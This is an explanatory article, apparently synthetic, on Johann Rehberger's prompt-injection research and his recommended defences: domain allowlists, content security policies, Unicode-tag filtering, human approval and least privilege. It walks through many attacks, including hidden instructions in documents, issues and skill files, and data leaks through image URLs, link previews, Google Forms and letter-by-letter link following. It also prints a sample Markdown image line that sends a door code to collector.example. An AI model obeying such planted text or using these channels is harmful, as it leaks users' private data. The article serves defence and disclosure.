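# Johann Rehberger's security advice for developers of AI applications

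## What does Rehberger advise, and what problem is the advice meant to solve?

Johann Rehberger is a security researcher who studies how outsiders can turn AI products against the people using them. His main subject is prompt injection, which is text that makes a language model follow instructions its user or developer did not give. Since 2023 he has reported prompt injection flaws to OpenAI, Microsoft, Google, Anthropic and many smaller companies, and he has given developers much the same advice throughout. He advises them not to load images or links from untrusted domains, and to set a browser rule that enforces this. He also advises them to filter out invisible characters, ask a person for approval before sensitive actions, and give AI systems little access from the start.

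Rehberger's background is in red teaming, which means attacking an organisation's systems with its consent to find weak points before real attackers do. According to the *Speaker Profile* from the Chaos Computer Club, a German hacker association, he set up a red team within Microsoft's Azure Data group, built another at Uber, and now directs the one at the games company Electronic Arts. He writes the blog Embrace The Red under the name wunderwuzzi. Its posts go back to 2018 and covered stolen cookies and passwords long before chatbots.

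Rehberger reports a flaw to the vendor before he writes about it. In Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, he describes telling Microsoft about a data leak in its chatbot on 8 April 2023 and publishing after he heard on 15 June that a fix was in place. On 4 December 2023 he told Google about a flaw in NotebookLM, a tool for analysing uploaded documents. Google confirmed the flaw but had not fixed it after 132 days, so he published a post about it, citing an industry norm of three to four months. In an update to that post, Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps*, he added that Google's team then contacted him directly and had deployed a fix for the image leak by 19 April 2024. Publication warns users, and in this case it probably also sped up the fix.

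### Hostile text in an ordinary document

Rehberger demonstrated an attack on the assistant built into Google Docs. The attacker writes instructions to the assistant in a shared file. When another person asks for a summary, the application sends the model the whole file along with the request. The model follows the planted instructions, and the reader gets a scam message urging them to call a phone number. Rehberger reported the attack to Google on 22 June 2023 and listed it as still unresolved in *Trust No AI* (2024), a paper that collects his findings.

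This is indirect prompt injection, in which the hostile text arrives in content the model reads, such as a web page, an email or a code file. In direct prompt injection, the user types the text, usually to get around the developer's instructions. Jailbreaking works against the model's training, so it doesn't need a developer's prompt to override. Most important for developers, the victim of indirect injection is the user, who may only have asked for a summary.

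An attacker needs to control only a small part of the text that an AI application reads. In the NotebookLM case, Rehberger imagined a company analysing its customer list, where one customer had put instructions in the description field of their own profile. Control of that one field was enough to reach the other customers' rows and a second document that the user had uploaded separately. On a web page, an attacker could use a comment or an advertisement. The instructions can be ordinary visible text. In an August 2026 interview, *How prompt injection attacks work*, published by 1P_nick (2026) on the forum of the password-manager company 1Password, Rehberger said that they are often just text in the middle of a document, where a reader is unlikely to notice them. He also pointed to a real-world attack known as Clinejection, in which an attacker used the title of an issue on the code-hosting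 site GitHub to hijack the AI system that processed it.

### Why the model cannot keep data and instructions apart

A language model keeps no record of earlier requests, so each time the user writes something, the application sends it one long text, called the context. The context holds the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions), the user's message, the conversation so far, any saved memories, and any pages or files the application has fetched. A developer can label these parts, and training can teach a model to favour some labels over others, but nothing forces the model to treat a given passage purely as data.

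A trust boundary is a line in a system across which data must be checked before anyone relies on it. The model's context has no such boundary within it. Rehberger applies this point in *Trust No AI* to developers who put secrets in the system prompt. The system prompt is inside the same trust boundary as the user's input, so users can often get the model to reveal the prompt.

Indirect injection gives a stranger the same reach. ChatGPT's chat-history feature puts information about past conversations in the system prompt. Rehberger explains in Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* that someone who writes a web page or PDF can therefore steal that history when the user asks ChatGPT to summarise it. Any feature that adds private material to the context increases what an injected instruction can reach.

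Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, in which an attacker types a fragment of database code into a form and a careless application pastes it into a query, where it runs. CERT.at (2025), Austria's computer emergency response team, recommends preventing this with prepared statements, which send the command and the user's text to the database separately so that it cannot confuse them. Language models have no equivalent. In his first explainer on the subject, Embrace The Red's *AI Injections*, Rehberger noted that most people's first idea is to stop mixing code and data, but that the way these models work makes this very difficult. He thought a closer comparison was social engineering, the manipulation of a person through plausible talk. Later, in *Trust No AI*, he said outright that prompt injection has no deterministic fix, meaning one that works every time.

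Newer models resist some attacks, but how well depends on where the hostile text appears. *DecodingTrust-Agent Platform (DTap)* (2026) tested agents, which are language models that carry out tasks by calling tools. In simulated legal work, agents treated a forged "partner directive" in a case file exactly like a genuine one. In finance tasks, the hostile text was in web pages, which agents were less likely to treat as authoritative, and only 18% of attacks succeeded. When Claude resisted, it ignored the planted instruction and finished the job, whereas GPT tended either to comply fully or to abandon the task. So a model can take into account how credible a passage looks. But an attacker can imitate credibility, and an 18% success rate is still high if the attacker can try repeatedly.

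### Treating the output as untrusted

Rehberger advises developers to treat all model output as untrusted and to have the application around the model limit what that output can do, rather than count on the model for protection.

Rehberger set out this advice on 15 April 2023 in Embrace The Red's *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots*, after building his own command-line assistant and chatbot. He argued that the danger depends on where the application puts the model's reply. In a web page, the reply might contain a script that runs in the visitor's browser. In a database query, it might change the query, and in a command line, it might run a program. Developers already knew these risks from text typed by strangers, and Rehberger was asking them to treat the model's text the same way. He also considered using a second model to supervise the first, but thought this an imperfect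 solution because the supervisor has the same weakness.

Six weeks later the premise had to cover actions as well as text, because OpenAI had given ChatGPT plugins that let it search for flights or read a user's email. In Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained*, Rehberger showed a web page causing ChatGPT to fetch the user's latest email and send a summary to an outsider. The page could not read the mailbox itself, so it used the access the user had granted ChatGPT. Security researchers call a program tricked into misusing its authority a confused deputy. Rehberger concluded that ChatGPT should not trust what plugins return, and that plugins should not blindly trust requests from ChatGPT. A tool call, which is a model's request that the application run a function, is therefore also untrusted output.

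Rehberger was blunter in later statements. In his December 2023 talk *New Important Instructions*, he said that a deterministic solution might never exist. In the 2026 interview, he advised developers to assume that a model can produce any text and make any tool call, and to run it in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits which files, credentials and networks a program can reach. He considered "prompt firewalls", which try to catch hostile text on its way in, less reliable than such controls. These filters make a successful injection less likely, but limits on the application still apply when one succeeds.

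Such limits also protect against a model's own mistakes. Rehberger observed in the same interview that an agent without the necessary access cannot carry out a harmful action, whether the cause is an error or an attack. He still distinguishes the two problems. Writing about a data leak that Anthropic had classed as a model safety issue, he said in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, "Safety protects you from accidents. Security protects you from adversaries." An adversary will look for the one case that a usually reliable model gets wrong.

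### How *Trust No AI* sorts the harms

By December 2024 Rehberger had enough cases to classify them. *Trust No AI* groups them by the three properties that security policies traditionally protect, known as the CIA triad: confidentiality, integrity and availability.

The largest part of the paper covers confidentiality, which means keeping private information private. Most of the cases involve data exfiltration, or sending private data to an outsider without authorisation. Rehberger lists eleven products in which he found that an image address could carry data out. He then covers links, tools and ChatGPT's long-term memory, where a planted instruction could persist and leak later conversations too.

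Integrity means guarding information against improper change. The Google Docs scam is an attack on integrity, as is an email that shows different text depending on who asks Microsoft's Copilot about it. Availability means a system is ready when someone needs it. An injected instruction can make an assistant refuse to summarise an email or, once stored in memory, refuse every later request. It might also start an endless loop of tool calls, although when Rehberger tried this on ChatGPT, he found that OpenAI had capped the loop at ten.

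The categories overlap. Invisible characters appear under integrity, for instance, though Rehberger notes that they have also helped to leak data. Sorting the cases still helps developers because it shows where the advice is weakest. An application can block requests to unfamiliar domains or tool calls that lack approval, but it has no comparable way to block a false sentence in a summary. For false statements, Rehberger found that vendors had settled on a notice that AI makes mistakes. He suggested that they also cite sources and look for ways to mark text the model had copied unchanged.

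### The five defences

The table gives the recommendations that recur through his posts, with the year in which he first made each one.

| Defence | Harm it limits | First advised |
|---|---|---|
| Do not load images or links from untrusted domains | Private data leaving inside a web address | 2023 |
| Set a content security policy (CSP), a rule telling the browser which domains a page may load content from | The same leak through images, stopped by the browser | 2023 |
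| Filter invisible Unicode characters and terminal control codes | Instructions or data that the user cannot see; interference with the user's terminal | 2024 |
| Ask a person before sensitive tool calls | Emails, purchases or changes of settings that the user did not want | 2023 |
| Give agents little access | The damage a hijacked or mistaken agent can do | 2023 |

Rehberger's oldest recommendations are human review and least privilege, which means giving a program only the access its task requires. Both appear in the April 2023 post, and he applied human review to tool calls in the plugin post of 28 May. In *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023), published on 16 May, he suggested only that OpenAI handle images through a dedicated feature. The unqualified rule against rendering images or clickable links to arbitrary domains comes from his report to Google that December.

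Rehberger seems to have taken the idea of a content security policy from Microsoft. When he retested Bing Chat in June 2023, his attack no longer worked, and he noticed that Microsoft had introduced such a policy. By the December talk, he was recommending one himself.

The two kinds of filtering followed discoveries by other researchers. Riley Goodside showed that models read Unicode tags, which mirror ASCII characters but are usually invisible on screen. Rehberger's *ASCII Smuggler Tool* (Embrace The Red) advised removing them from both prompts and responses. Later in 2024, Leon Derczynski described how models can produce ANSI escape codes, which a terminal executes as commands instead of displaying. Rehberger's *Terminal DiLLMa* (Embrace The Red) recommended encoding them by default so that they appear as harmless text.

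### The Month of AI Bugs

In August 2025 Rehberger combined the advice and the disclosure practice in a series called the Month of AI Bugs. Embrace The Red's *Wrap Up* lists 29 posts. Most are about coding agents such as Claude Code, GitHub Copilot, Cursor, Devin, Google Jules, Amazon Q Developer and Windsurf, which write and run software for developers. Others are about ChatGPT, research agents and the general-purpose agent Manus. Coding agents are an attractive target because, as he said in the 2026 interview, developers keep many passwords and access keys on their machines.

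Rehberger wanted the series to expose unresponsive vendors as well as raise awareness. He wrote on its home page, Embrace The Red's *The Month of AI Bugs* (2025), that vendors had fixed many of the flaws, but that he also wanted to show where they had been unresponsive, "to encourage accountability and timely action". Each post included notes on how the vendor had handled his report. The programmer Simon Willison, who followed the series as it came out, found "an alarming number" of cases in which the vendor had not fixed the flaw after 90 or 120 days. In *The Summer of Johann*, Willison (2025) thought that most of these products would lose much of their usefulness if the vendor fixed the flaw.

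Rehberger later brought the findings together in a conference paper, *Agentic ProbLLMs* (2026). One of the design failures he saw across vendors was that products relied on the model's own output as a security control, which he had warned about in April 2023.

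## How can an application stop images and links from leaking data?

Rehberger advises against loading images and links from untrusted domains because they can leak data. In an August 2025 post on Embrace The Red, he called this kind of leak one of the most common security flaws in AI applications. Chat interfaces load images automatically, and an image's address can carry text to whoever runs the server.

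Models usually format their replies in Markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and pictures. The interface converts the Markdown into HTML, the language of web pages, for the browser to display. Suppose a user has typed the door code 4417 into a conversation and then asks the assistant to summarise a web page. An attacker has planted instructions in that page, a technique called indirect prompt injection. The leak then takes four steps.

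1. The model follows the planted instructions and ends its reply with a Markdown image whose address contains the code: `![chart](https://collector.example/chart.png?note=4417)`
2. The interface turns that line into an HTML image tag with the same address.
3. The browser fetches the image as soon as it displays the reply, so it sends the full address to collector.example.
4. The attacker, who runs collector.example, reads 4417 in the server's log of requests.

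The user doesn't have to click anything and may not see the image, since the server can return a transparent picture one pixel wide. According to Embrace The Red, Rehberger used several such image requests to extract a larger amount of data from Google AI Studio, a tool for developers.

### Links and link previews

A clickable link can hold the same address, but the browser sends nothing until the user clicks, so the attacker has to give them a reason to. When Rehberger reported the NotebookLM leak to Google, he gave the example "Click here to re-authenticate". This is why his advice on Embrace The Red covers clickable links as well as images. NVIDIA, whose AI red team tests AI systems before they go into production, suggests that an application either show the whole address before it opens an outside site or make links inactive, so that the user has to copy and paste the address.

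When someone posts a link in a messaging service such as Slack or Discord, the service fetches the address without waiting for a click, so that it can show a title and a preview picture. Developers call this unfurling. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, passed on Rehberger's warning that a chatbot with access to private data could leak it just by posting a link.

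The following year, Rehberger found an example in a widely used connector, published by Anthropic, that let AI agents read and post Slack messages. An administrator could restrict it to a single private channel, and a user might then reasonably let the agent post without supervision. But Slack fetched any link in the agent's message, so text in the link's address still left the company.

Rehberger reported the problem on 27 May 2025. Anthropic archived the connector two days later, although he could not tell whether his report was the reason. In June, Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* warned that no patch would come, when the connector had more than 14,000 weekly downloads. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-34072* (2025), an entry in the Spanish cybersecurity institute's catalogue of flaws, rates the severity 9.3 out of 10, while Rehberger rated it 7.5.

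Users can fix the connector with two Slack settings that turn off link and media previews. Rehberger thinks previews should be off by default for any AI system that posts to a messaging service, with a list of approved domains for people who need previews. Some systems still leave them on. PromptArmor, a company that looks for security flaws in AI products, found that the agent OpenClaw was exposed to this kind of leak by default when people used it through Telegram.

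### Four ways to stop the request

The most reliable defence is to load no external images, which is what Google chose for AI Studio. Rehberger could not get a date for a fix through the company's official channel, so he raised the leak publicly with a Google employee. Within 24 hours the interface was displaying image tags as text, so the browser no longer requested the images and no data was sent to their addresses. With this defence, the assistant can no longer show images from elsewhere on the web.

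An application can still show some images if it uses an allowlist, which is a list of permitted domains. It loads images from those domains and refuses all others. The allowlist is only as safe as the least safe domain on it.

Asking the user before loading is weaker, because users often cannot tell what an address contains. Showing the full address helps, since 4417 would at least be visible, but an attacker can have the model encode the text so that users don't recognize it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) adds that frequent warnings can train people to click through without thinking.

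A content security policy backs up whichever of these measures an application uses. The server sends the policy with the page, and the browser enforces it. A rule for images might read:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://images.shop.example`

Here `'self'` means the site that served the page, and the second entry permits one other site. The image from collector.example matches neither entry, so the browser does not request it and the attacker does not receive the door code. The user sees at most a broken picture.

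The second barrier is useful because application code misses cases. Microsoft 365 Copilot filtered out images and links to outside sites, but its developers had overlooked an alternative Markdown syntax for them. Willison explained this in June 2025, after the security company Aim Labs published the flaw. The browser's policy should then have blocked the image, but it allowed every address under teams.microsoft.com, and one of those addresses forwarded requests to any other site.

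An `img-src` rule also covers only images that a browser loads into that page. It doesn't affect a link the user clicks, a preview Slack fetches, or a phone app that displays replies without a web page.

### When a permitted domain stores data for anyone

Superhuman, an email application with an AI assistant, had a content security policy that blocked unknown domains but permitted docs.google.com. Google Forms runs on that domain, and loading a web address that contains the answers submits a form. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes how a hostile email made the assistant write an image whose address pointed to the attacker's form and contained the text of other emails as the answer. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the form.

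The user had only asked for a summary of recent mail and did not need to have opened the hostile email. PromptArmor extracted parts of more than 40 emails in one reply. It reported the flaw to Superhuman on the night of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday, deployed a first patch on Tuesday and finished further repairs on 11 January 2026, a day before the two companies made the flaw public. PromptArmor ranked Superhuman's response among the best it had seen.

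A developer therefore needs to know whether a stranger can store data on a domain or read a record of the requests it receives, because the owner's reputation is a poor guide. Writer.com, an AI writing service, permitted cloudfront.net, where any customer of Amazon's delivery network can host files. Salesforce's policy still listed a domain whose registration had expired, so researchers at Noma Security registered it and received the leaked data. Salesforce corrected its policy and added a separate check to stop its agent from producing links to untrusted domains. A careful allowlist lists exact hosts, excludes any that accept uploads or form entries, and is rechecked as domains change hands.

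### Vendors that acted quickly

Rehberger reported on 12 July 2023 that an uploaded file could make Claude leak the user's conversation, and Anthropic closed the report on 26 July. Claude no longer loaded images automatically, and users had to click "Show Image" to see them. In Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Rehberger wrote that this stopped the automatic leak but was not perfect, and that he hoped for a better fix. The same leak existed in Claude's iOS app, and Willison (2024) quoted the announcement in December 2024 that Anthropic had fixed it there.

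Google's chatbot Bard already had a content security policy when Rehberger and two collaborators examined it, but the policy allowed all of google.com, including a service where anyone can run small scripts. Rehberger wrote a script there that copied incoming data into a document. He reported the leak on 19 September 2023, and Google confirmed a fix when he asked on 19 October. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* thanks Google for acting promptly. Rehberger could not work out what had changed, since the policy was the same and images still loaded, but he guessed that Google was now filtering data out of image addresses.

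By June 2024, GitHub had stopped its programming assistant, GitHub Copilot Chat, from loading images from untrusted domains. The timeline in Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* begins on 25 February that year. In *GitHub Copilot Chat*, Willison listed the flaw alongside similar ones in five other products. Rehberger later said that Microsoft, which owns GitHub, had fixed it promptly.

In 2025 the researcher Omer Mayraz found that, despite the fix, Copilot Chat could still leak secrets and source code from private projects (Underhill, 2025, *GitHub Copilot Flaw Allowed Silent Data Theft*). This time the images came through Camo, GitHub's own image server. According to Nudge Security, GitHub responded on 14 August 2025 by disabling images in Copilot Chat altogether.

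Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, leaked data through diagrams. It could draw them from a text notation called Mermaid, and they could include images from an outside server. Rehberger used this to extract access keys and the agent's stored memories. He noted that the diagram appeared directly, so the user had no chance to notice a long image address in the reply.

Cursor received his report on 30 June 2025, resolved it by 7 July and released the fix in version 1.3 on 29 July. In Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE*, he thanks the team for its speed. But in October, GCVE (2025), a public database of flaws, recorded that versions up to 1.6 still loaded images inside Mermaid diagrams. According to SentinelOne, version 1.7 fixed this. Either the July fix was incomplete or a later change undid it.

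A demonstration page that Rehberger had written long before worked against Amp, a coding agent from Sourcegraph. He contacted the company on 14 June 2025, and Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* praises the team for a quick fix.

### OpenAI's partial fixes

Rehberger told OpenAI about the leak in early April 2023, and OpenAI first acted in December. ChatGPT's web interface began sending an image's address to an OpenAI service before displaying the image, and the service classified the address as safe or unsafe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* called this a step in the right direction but reported several gaps.

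OpenAI did not publish the criteria for its check on image addresses, whereas anyone can inspect a content security policy. Rehberger tried 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them loaded, so short texts could still leak one character at a time. He suggested limiting the number of images in each reply. Willison (2023) linked to Rehberger's post under the same title and called the solution "half-baked". The check ran only in the web version at first, and Rehberger's timeline in *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* shows that the macOS app did not get it until September 2024.

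In October 2024 Rehberger reported that the check accepted domains where an outsider could read the server's logs. One was windows.net, where any Microsoft Azure customer can rent storage. The gap was still open the next summer, and he published it in August 2025 after OpenAI had not answered his questions about a fix for a month. He asked OpenAI to publish its list of safe domains and to let business customers set their own. OpenAI tightened the check around that time. In November The Hacker News (2025) reported that the check also trusted bing.com, including Bing's advertising links, which could disguise a hostile address.

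In January 2026, OpenAI described a stricter rule that checks exact addresses rather than whole domains. ChatGPT automatically loads an address only if OpenAI's web crawler has already found that exact address in public. The crawler has no access to conversations, so an address containing one user's door code should not be in its index. If there is no match, ChatGPT either looks for another source or warns the user. According to a separate OpenAI post, the warning shows the information that would go to the outsider.

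In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger called this a significant improvement but did not consider the problem solved. Someone with a large website already has plenty of public addresses and can assign a letter to each. Each request to one of 36 addresses conveys about five bits, so a series of requests can still spell out a short secret. He proposed that ChatGPT either refuse to visit the same address twice in a session or reuse a stored copy, which would make repeated letters harder to send.

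He also worried that developers elsewhere in OpenAI might not know about the protection or use it. A few months later, the original leak turned up in a newer OpenAI product. On 21 April 2026, PromptArmor reported that Codex, an agent for programming and office work, could leak a user's emails through an image and a Google Form, as Superhuman had. OpenAI had fixed the flaw by the time PromptArmor published *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* on 21 May. NVD's *CVE-2026-14898 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, describes the same flaw or a closely related one in the Codex app for macOS. OffSeq, which tracks such entries, lists version 26.527.31326 as the fix.

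### Cline and Windsurf

Rehberger reported the leak in Cline, another coding agent, on 29 May 2025. Nobody seemed to be reading the project's security reports, so after 35 days he pointed this out in a public ticket. The project closed the ticket the same day without discussing the flaw. He published *Cline* on Embrace The Red after more than 90 days, leaving out the core of the hostile text because users were still exposed.

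Rehberger advised Cline to block images from untrusted domains or ask the user before loading them, and to put someone in charge of security. He also suggested turning off automatic approval of the agent's actions by default. This would limit which files an attacker could make the agent read, but it would not protect a secret already in the conversation. Cline does not appear to have announced a fix since.

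Rehberger reported several flaws to Windsurf, a rival code editor, in May 2025. HiddenLayer (2025), a security company, reported another leak on 1 August, wrote again two weeks later and published on 17 October, having received no reply. By then Google had paid about $2.4 billion to license Windsurf's code, on which it based its own editor, Antigravity. When Antigravity came out in November, Rehberger found that it still had the flaws he had reported, as he wrote in Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*. Google listed data leaks as a known issue and said it was working on them. In 2026, Adversa AI's *Windsurf Agent Security Risks* found that Windsurf itself still loaded outside images with no list of permitted domains.

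### The same flaw in new applications

NVIDIA credits Rehberger with publicizing the leak in mid-2023, and its red team says it still finds the flaw in AI applications. NVIDIA's advice, which is close to his, is to set a content security policy for images, show users where links lead, and strip Markdown, HTML and web addresses from the model's output. It treats switching off all such active content as a last resort, presumably because users would lose the most.

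Reports from 2026 support NVIDIA's observation. GitLab's *CVE-2026-22551* (2026) describes the leak in Eclipse Theia, a platform for building code editors, whose AI chat loaded images from any address. Theia's developers responded by disabling AI features in projects that the user has not marked as trusted. PromptArmor (2026) reported an image leak in Notion's AI on 24 December 2025, and the report was marked "non-applicable" five days later. Notion did not contact PromptArmor until 7 January, the day PromptArmor publicly disclosed the leak.

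Microsoft's Copilot Cowork leaked data through email, outside the chat window. Willison described in May 2026 how the agent could email its own user without approval, and how opening such an email loaded its images. A developer therefore has to apply the image rule everywhere the model's text may appear, including the user's inbox.

### Limiting the addresses an agent may open

An agent with a tool for fetching web pages can leak data without displaying anything, because it can open the attacker's address itself. Under an Anthropic rule that Willison described on 10 September 2025, Claude could open an address only if the address had already appeared in the user's message, in search results, in a page Claude had fetched, or in the results of certain other tools. The software around the model enforces this rule, so even if an attacker persuades Claude to compose an address containing private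 data, Claude can't open it.

Willison thought the ban on composed addresses gave the most protection, but he pointed out that many applications paste outside text into the user's message, and the rule then treats any address in that text as the user's own. Developers can also restrict the tool to a list of domains, but they then have to find domains that no attacker can use to collect data. Google failed to do this in Antigravity that November, when the editor's browser tool could by default open webhook.site, where anyone can record incoming requests.

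Letting Claude follow links inside the pages it fetched proved to be a more serious gap. Ayush Paul built a site whose pages linked to further pages, one for each letter, and got Claude to spell out the user's name, home city and employer by choosing which links to follow. Claude never composed an address itself. Rehberger had found the same letter-by-letter leak in ChatGPT's image check in 2023. Anthropic told Paul that it already knew of the problem and paid him no bounty. By the time Willison wrote about the attack on 15 July 2026, Anthropic had closed the gap by stopping the tool from following links in the pages it fetches. The fix removed an ordinary part of web browsing, since Claude can now open a linked page only if the user supplies its address or a search returns it.

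## Which hidden characters should an application filter?

Rehberger's advice on hidden characters covers Unicode tags and ANSI escape codes. Unicode gives every character a number called a code point. The tags occupy U+E0000 to U+E007F and correspond to ASCII, the basic set of English letters, digits and punctuation. Adding hexadecimal E0000 to an ASCII character's code point gives its tag, so the tag for A (U+0041) is U+E0041. The door code 4417 from the earlier example becomes U+E0034, U+E0034, U+E0031, U+E0037. Most software displays nothing for these characters, not even a gap.

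On 11 January 2024, Goodside showed that invisible instructions in pasted text could make ChatGPT create an image. Cisco, which sells AI security products, traces the effect to the tokenizer, the component that cuts text into units for the model. The tokenizer splits each invisible character, called a tag, into a marker and the corresponding ordinary character, which the model then reads. Rehberger suspected that the training data had also contained tags.

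### Hidden data in a reply

Many models can write tags as well as read them. Rehberger called passing hidden messages this way "ASCII smuggling" in Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggling and Hidden Prompt Instructions*. An attacker who has hijacked an assistant can make it write private data in tags in a reply without the user noticing.

Rehberger demonstrated this on Microsoft 365 Copilot, as he explains in Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot*. A hostile email made the assistant search the user's mailbox for other messages, such as one containing login codes, and append their contents to a link as invisible tag characters. With the door code, the link would look like `https://collector.example/` on screen but carry 4417 after the slash. Showing the user the whole address, as NVIDIA suggests, helps only if the application also makes the invisible characters visible.

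Rehberger first reported Copilot's handling of tags on 17 January 2024, and Microsoft closed the report the next day as low severity. On 10 February he sent a complete attack that extracted sales figures, and Microsoft opened a case. By 2 July the attack no longer worked, and Copilot seemed to have stopped displaying links. Microsoft did not answer when he asked how it had fixed the flaw, so it is unclear whether Copilot began filtering tags.

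Invisible text also weakens human review. Someone who checks a document before giving it to an assistant, or an email before an agent sends it, can judge only the text they can see. Rehberger warned on Embrace The Red in January 2024 that attackers could get people to copy, forward or approve text containing hidden instructions.

### Removing the tags

The filter deletes every character from U+E0000 to U+E007F before text reaches the model, which removes hidden instructions. It does the same to the reply before the application displays it or passes it on, which removes any data the model has hidden there.

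Filtering out tag characters breaks a few emoji. The flags of England, Scotland and Wales each consist of a black flag followed by tag characters that spell out the region, such as "gbeng" for England, so only the black flag is left after filtering. In its guide *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling*, Amazon's cloud business AWS considers this a minor loss for most companies.

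The filter takes one line of Python, but AWS warns that a single pass can fail in Java. Java stores each tag as two halves, and an attacker can place a complete tag between the halves of another. When the filter deletes the inner tag, the outer halves join into a new tag. AWS's Java code therefore also deletes stray halves and repeats the process until the text stops changing.

### Other invisible characters

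An attacker can also hide text in invisible characters outside the tag range. Variation selectors normally choose between versions of a character, such as the plain and emoji forms of a heart. Paul Butler showed that a string of them can encode any data, because there are 256 of them, one for each value of a byte. In March 2025, Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* showed that any two invisible characters are enough if one represents 0 and the other 1. A basic letter then takes eight invisible characters.

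Rehberger therefore broadened his advice, recommending that developers remove invisible characters generally, flag messages that contain many of them, limit the length of prompts and replies, and write automated tests for the filter. But many emoji need variation selectors, and some languages use invisible marks to control text direction.

*Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) adds that Indic scripts use zero-width joiners, and recommends looking for the patterns that encoded messages produce rather than deleting whole categories of characters. Rehberger's scanner similarly gives a serious warning for a run of more than ten tag characters, or for more than 100 scattered through a file.

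Graves also measured how often models follow hidden text. He added invisible instructions to trivia questions, telling five models from OpenAI and Anthropic to give a different answer. Without a hint about the encoding or a tool for running code, the models gave the hidden answer at most 1.1% of the time. With both, Claude Opus 4 followed instructions in tags every time. GPT-5.2 almost never did, but it followed instructions written with two zero-width characters in about 70% of trials. A filter for tags alone would therefore have blocked few of the hidden instructions that GPT-5.2 followed.

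In two coding agents, Rehberger found that a short visible phrase just before the hidden text made the model more likely to follow it. Anyone who can write the document can include such a phrase, although a careful reader might notice it. This suggests that Graves understated the risk in reasoning that someone who controls only a document could not add the hints, which were in the system prompt.

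Variation selectors have worked against fewer products than tags. FireTail, which sells AI security tools, reports in *Peek a boo 🫣 emoji smuggling and modern LLMs* (2026) that the selectors worked against Gemini and, on a second attempt, Grok, but failed against ChatGPT, Claude, DeepSeek and Meta's assistant.

### Coding agents in August 2025

The Month of AI Bugs included four posts about coding agents that followed invisible text. Sourcegraph responded fastest. Rehberger contacted the company on 14 June 2025, after he used hidden instructions to make its agent, Amp, find an access key and send it out in a web address. Sourcegraph soon began cleaning the input, which he called "a simple and effective fix" in Embrace The Red's *Amp Code*.

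On 5 July, Rehberger reported the flaw in Amazon Q Developer, an extension with more than a million downloads, and on 8 August Amazon told him it had resolved the flaw. According to Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer for VS Code Vulnerable to Invisible Prompt Injection*, Amazon decided not to issue a public advisory, so users of older versions got no official warning to update.

Embrace The Red's *Google Jules is Vulnerable To Invisible Prompt Injection* describes a GitHub issue in which Rehberger visibly asked for a harmless code comment and invisibly asked for an extra function. The hidden text was copied to Jules with the rest of the issue. Jules included the function in its plan, approved the plan automatically, then added the code and ran it. Rehberger reported this on 26 May. When he repeated the demonstration on 15 August, Google had taken Jules out of beta and now let users assign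 it an issue just by adding a label. Google had still not fixed the vulnerability when he published.

The fourth product was Windsurf, which does not appear to have announced a fix. Google's Antigravity, which uses Windsurf's code, also followed hidden instructions when Rehberger tested it that November. One set came from a ticket in a project-tracking service, so the attacker did not need access to the developer's files.

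### Should the model provider or the developer filter?

Rehberger thinks model providers should remove tag characters before text reaches the model, because otherwise every application built on the model inherits the weakness. OpenAI does this, and in August 2025 he knew of no other provider that did. Graves's near-zero result for GPT-5.2 on tag characters is consistent with OpenAI removing them. Graves also considers filtering at the tokenizer the most robust defence, since the model never receives the hidden text.

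Google accepted Rehberger's report about Gemini as a valid bug in February 2024, when its models were still poor at reading tags. He found that Gemini 2.5 often followed instructions written in them in 2025, and that Gemini 3 was even better at it. But when FireTail reported the same weakness on 18 September 2025, Google replied that it would take no action, according to Cyber Security News.

Google's reason for not fixing the flaw, as quoted in BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*, was that the attack "can only result in social engineering" and that a fix would not make users less prone to such attacks. This is reasonable for a scam message, which an attacker could also write in visible text, but it doesn't fit the Jules case, where the agent ran hidden code without anyone being tricked. FireTail also used a calendar invitation to make Gemini show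 a false organiser and meeting link, even though the user had not accepted the invitation.

As Rehberger understood it, Anthropic did not intend to change how its models treat tags, which left developers to filter them. One practical argument for this is that developers are better placed than a model provider to know what their application needs. Cisco observes, for example, that whether losing flag emoji matters depends on the application. The argument is weak for tags, which have so little legitimate use, but stronger for zero-width characters, because removing them could damage text in entire languages.

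A developer has good reason to filter in either case, because the provider may not cover every encoding and the developer may later switch to a model from a company that filters nothing. Testing a provider's chat product also doesn't reliably show how its models behave elsewhere. FireTail found that the Claude chatbot resisted tags, but Rehberger had got them to work in Amazon Q, which runs on Claude models.

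### Skill files

In February 2026 Rehberger tested invisible text in skills, which are folders of written instructions that an agent loads when a task requires them. Anthropic introduced the format in October 2025, and other companies adopted it. Developers often install skills written by strangers, and cautious developers read the instructions first.

For Embrace The Red's *Scary Agent Skills*, Rehberger took a skill about security practices from OpenAI's public collection and added an invisible instruction to run a command. The file looked unchanged, but Anthropic's Claude Code ran the command when he used the skill. He had switched on automatic approval of commands for the demonstration.

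When Rehberger tried again on 10 February, Claude Code consistently detected the hidden text and refused to follow it. He could not tell whether Anthropic had deliberately added a defence. Skills on the claude.ai website had no such protection when he checked on 9 February.

He also scanned OpenAI's collection and the public library for the agent OpenClaw. The invisible characters there mostly belonged to emoji, and a few were test cases for security scanners. Nothing looked clearly malicious, although other people had already found many harmful skills. Some scanners for harmful skills did not look for invisible characters, so he published his own scanner and proposed adding a check to OpenClaw.

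### Terminal control codes

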